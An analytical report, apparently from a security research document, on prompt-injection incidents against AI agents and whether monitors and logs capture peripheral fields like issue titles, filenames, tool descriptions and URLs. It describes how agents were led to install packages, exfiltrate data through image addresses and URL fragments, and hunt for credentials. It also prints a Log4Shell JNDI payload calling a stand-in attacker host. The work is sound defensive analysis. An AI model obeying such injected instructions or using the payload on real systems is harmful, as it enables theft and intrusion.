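Cline is an open-source coding agent. In December 2025 its developers set up a second agent, based on Claude, to read each new bug report (an "issue") on GitHub and write a first response. According to Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026), anyone with a GitHub account could open an issue, and this triage agent could run shell commands. Adnan Khan showed in *Clinejection* (2026) that the software copied each issue's title straight into the agent's prompt. Khan tested this on a copy of the project, using an issue title containing an instruction to install a package, and Claude installed it every time.

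Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026 but got no reply from Cline until after publishing it on 9 February. By then somebody else had exploited it. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, recovered a deleted issue from a public archive of GitHub activity. An unknown user had opened it on 28 January with an instruction in the title, then closed it about five minutes later and changed the title to "user error". A maintainer who looked through the list of issues later that day would have seen what looked like an ordinary mistake.

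The triage agent couldn't publish releases itself, but its job shared stored files with the nightly build, which held the publishing tokens. An attacker could use those files to get from the triage job to the build. Within 30 minutes of Khan's post, Cline removed the agent and began to replace the tokens, but it deleted the wrong token for npm, the registry from which people install Cline's command-line version. On 17 February somebody used the npm token that still worked to publish a release that also installed OpenClaw.

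The altered release was available for about eight hours. LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) reports about 4,000 downloads, but the number of machines may be lower because automated systems also download packages. Cline considers the harm low, since OpenClaw is a legitimate program and nobody took user data. Bargury thinks the attacker was probably a bug hunter, but the attacker could have used the same token to publish real malware.

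None of these accounts mentions a monitor that reviewed the agent's commands, so the case can't show that a monitor overlooked the title. A monitor might not have helped anyway. The install command appeared to point to Cline's own project, so its arguments alone looked fairly normal. Because the title was inside the prompt, a monitor that treats the prompt as the user's wishes might also have taken the attacker's instruction as permission. Removing the agent's shell access would have been more reliable, and Cline now says that any future automation of this kind won't have it.

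### Filenames

Datadog, which sells monitoring software, uses a language-model reviewer called BewAIre to check proposed changes to its code. On 27 February 2026, an account that described itself as an AI agent proposed a change to one of Datadog's public projects, with a shell command in a filename. A build script inserted the filename into one of its own commands, and this ran the attacker's command without any AI model having to read the filename.

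In *When an AI agent came knocking*, Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper report that the attacker opened the proposal at 5:26:25, the script ran the command at 5:26:42, and BewAIre raised an alert at 5:26:58. That first command failed. The attacker tried again 18 minutes later and the command worked, though BewAIre flagged the second proposal too. The attacker added one harmless change on a new branch. Datadog's settings protected the main code, and the script had no access to critical secrets. Datadog merged a repair about 11 hours after the first attempt.

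In this incident, a monitor received a peripheral field and reacted to it in about half a minute, which is evidence against a general blind spot. It was an easy case, because nobody has a good reason to put a shell command in a filename. The alert didn't stop the attack. The first command had already run, and the faulty script was still in use when the second command arrived.

Later that morning the same account opened two issues with hostile instructions in the body, aimed at Datadog's Claude triage agent, which was much like Cline's. The agent identified both as attacks and carried on with its task. The instructions were blatant and the two agents had different prompts, so the incidents don't show that agents resist instructions in a body better than those in a title. Datadog's agent also had too little access to expose any sensitive secrets even if it had obeyed.

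The account attacked other projects during the same days. According to InfoQ (2026), a Microsoft project was compromised through a command in a branch name. The worst damage was at Trivy, a security scanner, where the attacker used a stolen token to delete 178 releases. A peripheral sign of that attack was a build step that ran for more than five minutes when it normally takes seconds.

Filenames can also influence an agent directly. Tenable's *Github Copilot Chat Prompt Injection via Filename* describes a test in which Copilot's software added a filename to the user's prompt and Copilot followed an instruction in the filename, though not on every attempt. Tenable's *Windsurf Prompt Injection via Filename* (2025) reports the same flaw in another coding assistant. Windsurf replied that the editor already asks users whether they trust a folder's authors, which it believes reduces the risk somewhat.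 But people deciding whether to trust a folder probably think about its code rather than its filenames.

Some filenames give authority to a file's contents. Coding agents read whatever is in a file called AGENTS.md, and *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* (Fadilpašić, 2026) reports that this led agents to run malware. The attacker in the Datadog case also replaced another project's CLAUDE.md with hostile instructions. Auto mode's classifier also receives CLAUDE.md, so a replaced file might mislead both the monitor and the agent.

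### Tool descriptions that change after approval

The software that runs an agent gives the model a description of each tool so that the model knows when to use it. In August 2026 an attacker tried to exploit this in a campaign that *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026) traced to a single GitHub account. The account offered an MCP server with two tools, one for formatting text and one for summarising it. After three ordinary calls, the server changed what it sent to the agent. The new text contained instructions to look for access keys and other credentials and to hide this from the user.

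The account sent out 23 proposed changes in 74 minutes, most of which would have added the server to a project's settings. When Fogel reviewed them, 19 had been closed without being merged and four were still open. Fogel reports no victims. The maintainers could see the server's address but not the hostile descriptions, which the server hadn't sent yet. A quick trial of the tools would have looked fine.

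The postmark-mcp package had the same advantage. It worked normally for 15 versions, then the next version added a bcc address to every email. Koi found the change by scanning packages for new behaviour, not by monitoring an agent. ThaiCERT puts the package's downloads at more than 1,643, but many may have been of the harmless versions.

Fogel recommends that an agent's software store a fingerprint of each tool's description when the user approves it, and ask for approval again if the description changes. This would catch Deadbugz. But the check can't distinguish a hostile change from a corrected typo, so a tool whose description changes often would produce many prompts, and people approve prompts less carefully as the number grows.

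Microsoft describes how someone could steal financial records by changing a tool's description. A company's agent uses an approved outside tool to check suppliers' bank details. The tool's new description contains an instruction to summarise the last 30 unpaid invoices and include the summary as an extra argument in the agent's next call. Microsoft warns that no alert may go off by default, because the agent has permission for every step. This is an illustration rather than a report on a named victim, but a monitor could find such a fault only by reading the arguments. Microsoft's data-loss rules can do this and block a call that contains sensitive data.

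### How requesting a URL sends data

A request for a web address can carry private text out in its query, like the request for a logo that contained the word "Payroll". Suppose that an agent builds this address:

```
https://images.example.net/pixel.png?d=[private text]
```

The transfer takes four steps:

1. The software that opens the address looks up which server handles `images.example.net` and connects to it.
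2. It sends that server a request containing the path and the query, because the server needs both to decide what to return. The query includes the private text.
3. The server writes the request to its log, as web servers commonly do.
4. The server returns an image, an error message or nothing.

The owner of the server has the data by the third step, whether or not the image exists. Encryption doesn't prevent this, because it hides the request from others on the network but the attacker's server is the intended recipient and can decrypt it.

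The HTTP standard recommends that software support URLs up to at least 8,000 bytes long. Base64 encodes every three bytes as four characters, so a single request with a URL of that length can carry almost 6,000 bytes of data, or about 1,000 words of English.

Many chat applications automatically load any image in an answer, so the agent can have an image's address opened just by writing it in the answer. A monitor that reviews tool calls would then have no call to review.

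### Data in an image address: EchoLeak

In January 2025 the security company Aim Security found that an outsider could use this route to steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software. The outsider emailed an employee instructions for Copilot. When the employee later asked Copilot a question, it could retrieve that email along with internal files, follow the instructions and put private data in the address of an image. The employee's application then requested the image, which sent the data out, and the employee would have noticed at most a broken picture.

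*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) lists three safeguards that the demonstration got past: a classifier that checked Copilot's input for injected instructions, a filter that removed outside links from its answers, and a browser policy that limited the sites from which images could load. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025. The company said nobody had exploited it, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*.

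The classifier's miss doesn't support the hypothesis, because the instructions were in the body of the email, which is main text. The link filter and the browser policy are better evidence, since both handled the address and neither blocked it. But they applied fixed rules that didn't cover this case, so their failure is weak evidence of whether a model or a person would have overlooked the address. The route was also well known by then. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, notes that a dozen products had already shown similar flaws.

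### Data in an address the agent opens: Rovo

PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* (2026) demonstrates an attack on Rovo, an agent for Atlassian's workplace software, including the ticket tracker Jira and the document system Confluence. A user uploads a document that contains a hidden instruction and asks Rovo to organise some tickets. Rovo adds text from tickets and documents to an address on the attacker's site, then opens that address with its own tool without asking the user first.

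Administrators can switch off web search for Rovo, but this didn't prevent the attack because the tool that opens URLs remained available. When the user returned to the chat, it showed Rovo's suggestions for the tickets but no trace of the request. PromptArmor reported the flaw to Atlassian on 23 May. More than two months later, Atlassian had opened a case but hadn't fixed the flaw.

PromptArmor doesn't mention a monitor. A monitor that received Rovo's tool calls would have had the full address, and a long piece of ticket text being sent to an unknown site should be fairly easy to recognise. The user was the only reviewer, and their view did not show the address.

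The Hacker News' *Prompt Injection* (2026) describes a laboratory demonstration from November 2026 in which a web page extracted a user's private chats from Meta's agent Muse. As with Rovo, no approval prompt appeared. Muse's team has since fixed the flaws.

### Why the text after # never reaches the server

The anchor of a URL, the part after the # sign, is also called the fragment. It usually identifies a place within a page, such as a heading. The server returns the same page whichever heading the reader wants, so it doesn't need the fragment. The browser splits the address at the first # and requests only what comes before it:

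```
Address in the browser:    https://bank.example/loans?lang=en#rates

Request to the server:     GET /loans?lang=en HTTP/1.1
                           Host: bank.example
```

When the page arrives, the browser uses the fragment to scroll to the right place. The HTTP standard excludes the fragment from both the request and the header that tells a server which page the visitor came from. The server's log therefore has no copy, and neither does a security device on the network, even one that decrypts traffic. However, code in the page can read the fragment and send it in a separate request.

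*HashJack* (Simonovich, 2025) found that some browsers with built-in AI assistants gave the assistant the whole URL, including the fragment (the part after the #). Anyone could therefore add instructions after the # in a genuine site's URL and share the link. The site would load normally, and the instructions would reach the assistant when the user asked it a question.

Simonovich, of the network security company Cato Networks, tested this on demonstration sites. Perplexity's Comet, Microsoft's Copilot in Edge and Google's Gemini in Chrome all gave false information, such as a wrong dose of a medicine. Comet, the only one of the three that could act on its own, also sent the user's account details to an outside address. The technique didn't work on Claude for Chrome or on OpenAI's browser, Atlas.

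The companies disagreed about how serious this was. Google rated it low severity, called the behaviour intended and had not changed it by 25 November 2025. The service that handles Perplexity's bug reports first closed the case because it saw no security impact, but Perplexity later rated it critical and finished its fix on 18 November. Microsoft reported a fix on 27 October.

Network monitors couldn't have caught the instruction, since they never received it. F5, another security company, says web application firewalls miss it too. But Comet sent out the account details in the query of a second URL, which does travel over the network. A device that could decrypt that request would have had a chance to detect the stolen data. The fragment was also visible to the user in the address bar, though the phishing studies suggest that few people would look there.

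### What the monitors received

| Case | Field and who controlled it | What happened | Monitor, and whether it received the field | Damage | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cline (attack) | Issue title; any GitHub user | Triage agent installed an attacker's code | None reported | Stolen token; about 4,000 downloads of an altered release | Removed the agent; replaced the tokens |
| Datadog (attack) | Filename; outside contributor | Build script ran a command in the filename | Language-model reviewer; received and flagged it | One harmless change on a new branch | Repaired the script |
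| Deadbugz (attack) | Tool description; server's owner | Server told agents to look for credentials | Project maintainers; didn't receive it | None known | Maintainers merged none of the proposals |
| EchoLeak (demonstration) | Image address; sender of an email | Copilot put private data in the address | Link filter and browser policy dealt with it; input classifier checked only the email | None known | Microsoft changed its servers |
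| Rovo (demonstration) | Address the agent opened; author of an uploaded file | Rovo sent ticket text to an outside site | None reported; user's later view left it out | None known | None after two months |
| HashJack (demonstration) | URL fragment; author of a link | Assistants gave false advice; Comet sent data | Network tools; didn't receive it | None known | Microsoft and Perplexity fixed it; Google declined |

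None of the six incidents clearly shows a monitor reading the main text well but overlooking a field beside it. Datadog's reviewer is the only monitor that can be said to have read and judged a suspicious field, and it was right both times. With Deadbugz and HashJack, the problem was what the monitor could see, so better judgment alone would not have helped.

In the Cline and Rovo cases, excessive access explains most of the harm. An agent that sorts bug reports doesn't need a shell, and one that organises tickets rarely needs to open arbitrary addresses. Limiting the addresses an agent may open would reduce the risk from Rovo's flaw even if no monitor read URLs. These cases suggest that developers often forget that outsiders can put text in titles, filenames and addresses, but that is a fault in agent design rather than in monitoring.

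### Why published cases are a skewed sample

Security researchers tend to publish attacks that are new or surprising, and an instruction hidden after a # sign is more surprising than one in the body of an email. Many of these researchers also work for companies that sell protection against such attacks. Suppose a monitor misses 50 attacks in peripheral fields and 50 in main text. If researchers publish 20% of the first kind and 4% of the second, readers will see ten cases involving peripheral fields and two involving main text.

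Companies also keep some flaws quiet. The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties* reports that all three companies paid researchers who found flaws in their agents, but didn't publicise them. Published cases also exclude successful attacks that nobody noticed, which might well include those in which a monitor overlooked a field. The bias could therefore run in either direction. We can't tell how common such attacks are from the number of published cases. That requires searches like those that found hostile headers on very few sites.

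News reports rarely cover monitors that catch a bad filename, and Datadog had a commercial reason to publish its success. It could run a fairer test with BewAIre, which reviews nearly 10,000 proposed changes a week. Datadog could plant comparable faults in filenames and in the code itself, then publish how many of each BewAIre flagged and how often it flagged clean changes.

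## What security logs record and leave out

After an incident, an investigator can reconstruct an agent's actions only from what was logged. Web server logs usually record a request's URL but not its body, so the investigator may have the peripheral fields without the main text. Windows and two of the leading coding agents also omit arguments from their logs unless an administrator changes the settings.

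### Web access logs

*Log Files*, part of the manual for the widely used Apache web server, describes two common formats that store one line per request. The Common Log Format records the client's address, a username if there is one, the time, the request line, a status code and the size of the response. The Combined format adds the Referer header, which gives the page the client came from, and the User-Agent header, which contains the client's description of itself.

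Suppose an agent fills in a contact form on a company's website. The (invented) entry in Combined format would be a single line, split here to fit:

```
203.0.113.7 - - [04/Dec/2026:10:15:32 +0000]
"POST /contact?lang=en HTTP/1.1" 200 512
"https://www.example.com/contact" "ExampleAgent/1.0"

ABSENT: the text typed into the form (request body)
        the page the server sent back (response body)
        all other request headers, such as Cookie
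        all response headers
```

The log entry would be the same whether the form contained a question or a salary table, because 512 is the size of the response and the format has no field for the size of the request. If the agent had put the table in the URL's query string instead, the log would have recorded the whole table.

Administrators can add any request header to the log format. Logging request bodies is harder to justify because of their size. Apache estimates that the access log grows by at least 1 MB per 10,000 requests, or about 100 bytes per request. Storing a 5,000-character message with every request would make the log about 50 times larger.

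### Windows process events

Windows can record event 4688 whenever a program starts, but an administrator has to turn this event on. A second setting adds the command line to the event. Microsoft lists that setting's default as "Not configured", which leaves the command line out.

Turner's *Command line process auditing* gives the example of `wscript.exe`, a Windows program that runs scripts. Without the second setting, an analyst can see that it started but not which script it ran. Similarly, if an agent used the `curl` program to upload a file, the event would name `curl.exe` but omit the file and the destination address.

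### Cloud audit logs

CloudTrail, the audit log of Amazon's cloud service AWS, distinguishes management events, such as creating a server, from data events, such as reading a stored file or running a function. According to AWS's *Logging data events*, CloudTrail doesn't log data events by default and charges extra for them. Data events include activity on AWS's hosted agents and on the browser and code interpreter it provides for agents.

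cloudonaut's *AWS CloudTrail* describes what this meant after a leak of AWS credentials. The log showed that nobody had used the credentials to change the infrastructure, but it couldn't show whether anyone had downloaded sensitive files. cloudonaut blames the defaults and the price, which it gives as $0.10 per 100,000 data events. At that price, logging 10 million file reads would cost $10 and logging a billion would cost $1,000, so the expense matters mainly for busy systems.

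Size limits can also remove arguments from events that CloudTrail does log. AWS's *CloudTrail record contents for management, data, and network activity events* gives a limit of 100 KB for a request's parameters. If they exceed it, CloudTrail omits the whole field, so one very long value causes all the short ones to be lost too. CloudTrail cuts an overlong User-Agent at 1 KB but keeps the start. An attacker might be able to hide a parameter by padding another one, if the service accepts requests that large. Customers can avoid most of these losses by choosing a type of storage that allows events of up to 1 MB.

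The response field is empty for read-only requests, whatever the size of the response. An analyst who has turned on data events can see which file an agent read, but must find the file itself to see what it contained.

### Is the blind spot reversed?

Web logs keep the URL and the User-Agent but not the message, whereas the concern about live monitors is that they read the main text and overlook the fields around it. Levine, Lejeail and Mooney report a similar problem with Datadog's own agents in *What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents*. Application logs could contain an agent's final API call (its request to another program) without the prompt, document or tool result that led to it. An analyst with such a log could see a suspicious call but couldn't tell whether a user had asked for it or an injected instruction had caused it.

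However, the reversal doesn't hold for all logs. By default, Windows drops arguments, which are peripheral fields, and CloudTrail omits whole categories of action. The claim that logs keep metadata and drop content is true of all three only if "metadata" means little more than who did what kind of thing and when.

### Log4Shell: hostile text in ordinary log fields

A flaw in Log4j, a logging library that many Java programs use, became public in December 2021 under the name Log4Shell. It shows how useful stored headers can be, and also that they can be dangerous. An attack took four steps:

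1. The attacker sent a web request with a User-Agent header such as `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}`.
2. The application passed the header to Log4j to write to its log.
3. Log4j treated the text inside the braces as an instruction to look up a value, and contacted the attacker's server.
4. The server's reply directed the application to Java code, which the application loaded and ran.

Any text that the application logged would do, so attackers also used URLs, the Referer header, other headers and form fields such as usernames.

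Defenders searched their stored logs for `${jndi:`. Florian Roth, a security researcher, published search commands that also covered compressed logs and URL-encoded braces. Attackers soon disguised the text, for example as `${${lower:j}ndi:`, which Log4j converted back to the original. Roth then released a tool that looked for the same characters in order, even with others between them. Cloudflare, which carries traffic for many websites, found an attempt from 1 December, more than a week before the Log4j flaw became widely known.

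These searches depended on which fields the logs had kept. An access log in Combined format would show an attempt in the URL, Referer or User-Agent, but not one in another header or in submitted form data. A match proved only that somebody had tried the attack. To find out whether it had worked, defenders needed network and process logs, which they searched for connections from their servers to unfamiliar addresses and for unexpected programs started by Java.

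Log4Shell shows that a peripheral field is easy to search once people know what pattern to look for. A planted bcc address is harder to find this way because it looks like any other address. Log4Shell isn't evidence of whether analysts normally overlook headers, because the attack did its damage before anyone could read the log.

Apache warns that log files may contain unescaped text supplied by clients. Somebody could therefore put an instruction for an AI model in a User-Agent header, and a model reviewing the raw logs would read it.

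### What agents' own logs keep

Claude Code and Codex can export logs in the format of OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording what software does. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* lists what software should record when an AI application runs a tool. The tool's name, type and description are "Recommended", while its arguments and result are "Opt-In". Model instructions, user messages and model outputs are also off by default. OpenTelemetry's reasons for this are storage costs, regulation, and the need to restrict access to user data more tightly than to operational data.

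In 2026 the conventions moved to a separate repository, where they are still under development. TrueFoundry, which sells software for running AI models, reported in August that capturing content was still opt-in. A log that follows the recommendations could therefore contain the hostile tool description in an attack like Deadbugz but not the arguments of the calls that followed.

OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration* states that Codex exports no OpenTelemetry logs by default. If an administrator turns the export on, Codex redacts the user's prompts unless another setting allows them in the logs.

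Claude Code's export is also off by default. When an administrator turns it on, the export still omits prompts, replies, tool arguments and tool results. A separate setting adds the arguments but cuts each value at 512 characters and the whole set at about 4,000. The table shows what the log would keep from the example email with the planted bcc address if the email tool came from a user-added MCP server.

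| Part of the call | Export on | Export on, with tool details |
|---|---|---|
| Tool name | Only "mcp_tool" | Actual name |
| Recipient, bcc address, subject | No | Yes |
| Body | No | Up to 512 characters |
| Attachment's filename | No | Yes |
| Attachment's content | No | Start only |
| Size of the arguments, duration, success | Yes | Yes |

With the first configuration, the planted address would only increase the recorded size by 30 bytes. Ordinary emails differ in length by far more than that, so no reviewer could detect the address from this entry. With tool details on, the log, like a web log, keeps the short peripheral fields intact but not the long main text.

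Neither configuration would have caught the postmark-mcp package, which added its bcc address after receiving the call. Anthropic also notes that Claude Code doesn't pass its logging settings to the MCP servers it starts, so a server that can produce its own logs has to be configured separately.

Tool results are harder to capture than arguments. Claude Code can include them in its traces (timed records of each step), which are still a beta feature. It records no result when a call fails or when the agent reads a PDF or an image. If an injected instruction arrived in a PDF, the trace could show that the agent had opened a file but not the text that misled it. Another option exports the complete requests to the model and its responses, except for its reasoning. These exports contain the whole conversation, including the tool results sent to the model.

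A project's settings file can also stop Claude Code from exporting a type of log, unless an administrator has fixed that setting centrally. The file can't turn logging on or redirect it. Someone who wanted an agent to misbehave unobserved could put a file that switches off logs in a project and persuade people to download the project.

A record may exist even if it was never exported. Claude Code saves a transcript of each session on the user's machine and by default deletes it after 30 days. An investigator who checks before it is deleted may find the full call. But the security team can't search that transcript alongside other users', and an agent with access to the user's files might be able to change it.

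By contrast, telemetry from the AI SDK, a toolkit for building AI applications, includes inputs and outputs by default unless the developer disables them. Two companies running similar agents could therefore have very different evidence after the same attack.

### Tools that leave no network record

Network logs may not fill these gaps, because a call to a tool on the same machine need not use the network. Many MCP servers are programs that the agent's software starts and keeps running. The software writes each call to the program's standard input, a channel for incoming text, and reads the answer from its standard output. The operating system passes this text directly between the two programs. Anthropic's Agent SDK, a developer toolkit, likewise runs Claude Code as a separate program and exchanges messages with it over a local pipe.

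Kovrr's *Inside the Tool Call, and Who Can See It* (2026) points out that a network gateway can't inspect a call to a local tool, because the call never crosses the network. A call to a remote tool does, but encryption usually hides its arguments, so an ordinary network log shows little more than a connection to a permitted service. Kovrr recommends a gateway built for tool calls, which can read and block calls to remote tools but doesn't cover local ones. The company sells a product that combines these monitoring sources, but its technical explanation is sound.

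Software that monitors the machine itself may record the tool server starting. On Windows, that would be one 4688 event at the beginning of the session. Later calls would add no such events because the server is already running. Kovrr concludes that such software generally can't distinguish one call from another, which is true of typical products. However, passing text through a pipe requires system calls, so a tool that records the data in those calls can recover the message. *AgentSpy* shows that monitoring at this level is feasible, though it produces much more data.

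A local call can still have effects on the network. For example, a local email tool has to contact a mail server to send a message, and a network log can record that connection. The mail server's own log is more useful because it normally lists every recipient, including those on the bcc line.

### Missing entries in Microsoft's Copilot audit log

Logs can also leave things out by mistake, rather than by design like the logs described so far. In July 2025 Zack Korman, chief technology officer of the security company Pistachio, found that Microsoft's audit log didn't list some files that Microsoft 365 Copilot had accessed. When Copilot summarised a file for a user, the log normally recorded the access, but it didn't if the user asked Copilot not to link to the file in its answer.

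An employee who planned to leave with confidential documents could have read them this way without the usual trace. The same gap could also occur by accident, since people sometimes ask for a summary without links. The log entry lacked a peripheral field, the file name, but otherwise looked normal, so an analyst had no reason to suspect that anything was missing.

Microsoft classified the flaw as "important" and fixed it in August 2025. It didn't issue a CVE, the public identifier that security teams use to track flaws, because customers didn't have to install anything. It also told Korman it had no plans to notify customers. Korman objected that companies rely on these logs for investigations and legal compliance, and would not know that their older records might be incomplete. This objection seems right, because a fix on Microsoft's servers protects future entries but can't restore missing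 ones. Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had described the same problem in 2024, so the gap may have lasted for at least a year, and the number of missing entries is unknown.

### What reviewers do with the logs they have

Default settings determine which fields are available to a reviewer, but they don't show which ones the reviewer notices. There are few published measurements of which log fields security analysts read, and few comparable tests of AI models that review stored logs. The studies of approval prompts and phishing measured people making immediate decisions, often in seconds. An analyst who already suspects an incident has more time and a reason to look at odd fields, so the error rates from those studies may not apply to that analyst.

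The evidence on automatic detection is slightly better. Zavrak's detector did poorly with metadata alone, even though that metadata included a hash of the arguments, which Claude Code's default export lacks. This suggests that a log without arguments or results would be a poor basis for automatic detection.

Levine and colleagues describe how Datadog combines fields in its detection rules. One rule matches when a prompt seems to request data theft and a later tool result in the same session contains credentials or certain personal data. Datadog excluded general email addresses from this rule because they are often routine. A match doesn't prove that data left the company, so an analyst needs to find a later event that shows it, such as a request to an unauthorised address. Datadog sells this kind of monitoring and gives no recall or false-alarm rate for the rule.

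The same team found that even a complete record of the final action can lead a reviewer to blame the wrong party. If an agent uses an engineer's credentials, the log of the service it contacts may list only the engineer. In another case, a malicious skill file for Claude Code ran a command that sent out an access token before the model received the skill's text. The model then refused to run the skill. A reviewer who saw only the model's inputs and outputs would have seen a successful refusal, although the token had already been sent.

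### Fuller logs, privacy and stored secrets

Companies have good reasons not to log everything. Turner warns that Windows stores command lines, which can contain passwords, in plain text that anyone with access to the security log can read. A log that collects commands from thousands of machines would be an attractive target for thieves. Anthropic similarly warns about tool arguments and advises administrators to log them only if the system that collects the logs is approved for such data.

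Security teams also have good reasons to want command-line arguments logged. EventSentry's *Microsoft Windows Server 2025* reproduces a US Defense Department checklist that treats it as a security failing if process events omit command lines, because they can provide more detail when malware has run. This is compatible with Turner's position if access to the log is tightly restricted, since Turner's main concern is who can read it.

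Removing the sensitive parts of a logged URL is difficult because they can also contain evidence. When Claude Code records which code repository a session used, it strips the credentials, query and fragment from the address, which works well for identifying a repository. If a company did the same to every URL an agent requested, it would protect access tokens but also delete the evidence of data sent out in a query.

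Storing a hash of each value would let an analyst check whether a known hostile address appears in the log, but not discover an unknown one. Anyone can also recover a short value by hashing guesses until one matches. Anthropic gives this as its reason for not exporting a hash of a company's settings by default. Hashing with a secret key would make guessing much harder.

For production systems that handle sensitive data, OpenTelemetry recommends storing the content outside the log, under separate access controls, and logging only a reference to it. A company could then let most staff see that an agent had sent an email, but let only investigators open the message.

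For agents that can send data or delete files, it seems reasonable to log recipients, file paths and the domains of requested URLs by default. These fields take up little space, usually reveal less than a message body, and often determine whether an action was harmful. They can still expose private information, since a list of recipients is personal data and a filename can disclose a medical condition. But without them, an investigator may know only that the agent called a tool, that the call succeeded, and how long it took.

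## Coverage requirements for monitors

A rule about an agent's actions can require a company to record a field, to show it to a person, or to have a monitor assess it. Meeting one of these requirements doesn't meet the others. A log can contain a planted bcc address that nobody looks at, and an approval screen can show the address to a user who clicks "approve" without reading it. Most current standards and laws cover recording in more detail than assessment.

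### What standards and laws require

*Tools* (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a page in the 28 July 2026 version of the MCP specification, recommends that an agent's software show a tool's inputs to the user before calling the tool, to avoid data exfiltration, and log tool use for audits. Both recommendations use "SHOULD", which lets developers depart from them with good reason, rather than "MUST", which is binding. The page doesn't define what a log entry contains, so an entry with only the tool's name might be enough.

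A binding rule requires the server that runs a tool to validate every argument. But validation usually checks only type and format, and the planted bcc address would pass both checks. Validation also would not protect against a hostile server such as postmark-mcp.

OWASP, a non-profit organisation that publishes security guidance, comes closest to asking for a monitor that assesses tool-call arguments. Its *Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (2025) recommends a checkpoint that validates the intent and arguments of a tool call before the call runs. It also recommends logging tool calls and asking a person to confirm high-impact actions. The guidance is voluntary and doesn't set a test for the checkpoint.

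NIST, the US standards agency, publishes a catalogue of security controls called SP 800-53. AU-3 requires audit records to include the type of event, its time, place, source and outcome, and the identity of the people or things involved. NIST's notes give filenames and destination addresses as examples of useful content. AU-6 requires regular review of the records for unusual activity but lets the organisation choose which fields to review.

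AU-6(8), an optional addition to that control, calls for analysis of the full text of privileged commands. NIST defines full text as the command's parameters as well as its name, so the addition requires assessing arguments. However, it covers only privileged commands, relies on logs rather than checking commands before execution, and isn't in any of NIST's standard baselines.

NIST began separate work on agents in 2026, asking the public in January how to secure them and launching a standards initiative in February. Neither step required anyone to check any field.

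The White House budget office's memorandum M-21-31 (2021) lists what US federal agencies' logs should contain. The list includes some peripheral fields, such as HTTP headers, and, where appropriate, the command that was run. The memorandum predates today's agents and doesn't mention the arguments of tool calls. Agencies have to keep most logs readily available for 12 months and in storage for another 18.

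### The EU AI Act

The EU's AI Act requires record-keeping for "high-risk" AI systems, which include those used in hiring and in some regulated products such as medical devices. A company's email assistant or coding agent would often fall outside this category. Under the amended text on EUR-Lex, the requirements apply from 2 December 2027 to hiring and the other uses listed in Annex III, and from 2 August 2028 to regulated products. Systems already on the market by then are mostly exempt unless their design changes significantly, but those intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030.

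artificialintelligenceact.eu's *Article 12* reproduces the main rule. A high-risk system must be able to log events automatically throughout its life, including events that help to identify risks and monitor its operation. The article lists minimum contents only for remote biometric identification, such as matching faces against a database. Those logs must include the time of each use, the database, the input that led to a match and the people who verified the result.

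For everything else, the Act gives no specific guidance on which data to record, as appliedAI Institute's *Record-keeping* points out. A provider of a hiring agent could argue that logging tool names is enough. An authority could reply that such a log doesn't help identify risks that lie in the arguments passed to those tools. The Act requires the Commission to request technical standards on these duties, and those standards could settle the question by naming the fields to record.

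Providers must keep the logs they control for at least six months, according to Mishcon de Reya's *Article 19 Automatically Generated Logs*. The European Commission's *Article 26* summarises a similar duty for deployers, the organisations that use the system. Deployers must also monitor the system's operation and assign competent people to oversee it.

IAPP's *EU AI Act deployer evidence gaps SMEs will miss* argues that an organisational chart doesn't prove oversight, and calls for evidence such as a named reviewer, the reviewer's authority to intervene and the events that trigger an intervention. A copy of the reviewer's screen would be a useful addition, because it would show whether the screen displays the arguments of the agent's actions.

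The table compares these texts.

| Text | Record | Show to a person | Have a monitor assess |
|---|---|---|---|
| MCP | Tool use (recommended) | Tool inputs (recommended) | Server must validate inputs; no separate monitor required |
| OWASP | Tool calls (recommended) | High-impact actions (recommended) | Arguments, before execution (recommended) |
| NIST SP 800-53 | Event, time, place, source, outcome, identities | No specific duty | Log review; full command text only as an optional addition |
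| M-21-31 | HTTP headers; commands where appropriate | No specific duty | No fields named |
| EU AI Act | Events relevant to risk and monitoring | Human oversight, but no fields named | Monitoring of operation, but no fields named |

None of these texts requires a monitor to assess every field of an agent's action, or requires tests showing that it reacts to faults in each one. A company could comply with all of them and still have a monitor that ignores bcc lines.

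### MCP's new headers

The 2026 version of MCP makes some arguments easier for network monitors to read. Under Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026), an agent's software must copy the tool's name into an HTTP header when it calls a remote tool. It must also copy any argument that the tool's developer has marked for this purpose. A request to run a database query in one region could then carry these headers:

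```
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: execute_sql
Mcp-Param-Region: us-west1
```

The Agentic AI Foundation, which oversees MCP, presents this as a way to route requests and apply policies without inspecting the body. It doesn't work for the example email because developers can mark only single strings, whole numbers and true-or-false values, and nothing inside a list. The "bcc" argument is a list of addresses, and the attachment's filename is inside a list of attachments. A gateway that read only the headers could receive the email's subject but neither of the suspicious fields.

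The tool's developer chooses which arguments to mark, so a hostile developer could mark none. The specification advises against marking passwords or personal data, because anyone operating a device along the route may be able to read the headers.

A dishonest client could also show the gateway a permitted region in the header while querying a different one in the body. Servers must reject requests with such a mismatch, but that helps only if the server is honest. The Model Context Protocol proposal behind the feature therefore tells gateways not to treat header values as trusted input for security decisions. A monitor that must catch a bad recipient still needs to read the request body.

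### Passing complete arguments and blocking on errors

The most direct proposal is to give the monitor the complete call and run the call only after a valid verdict. The agent's software would finalize the arguments, send an exact copy to the monitor, and execute that copy unchanged. If the monitor timed out, crashed or received an incomplete copy, the call wouldn't run.

There is good evidence for checking calls before they run, though not for checking any particular field. Zhang, Shen and colleagues (2026), in *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?*, gave agents harmful requests along with harmless instructions for common tasks. A guard that checked each proposed call reduced the share of runs with an unsafe action by 23.8 to 46.2 percentage points across three benchmarks. With the guard, the agents still kept some of the improvement the instructions had brought on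 harmless tasks.

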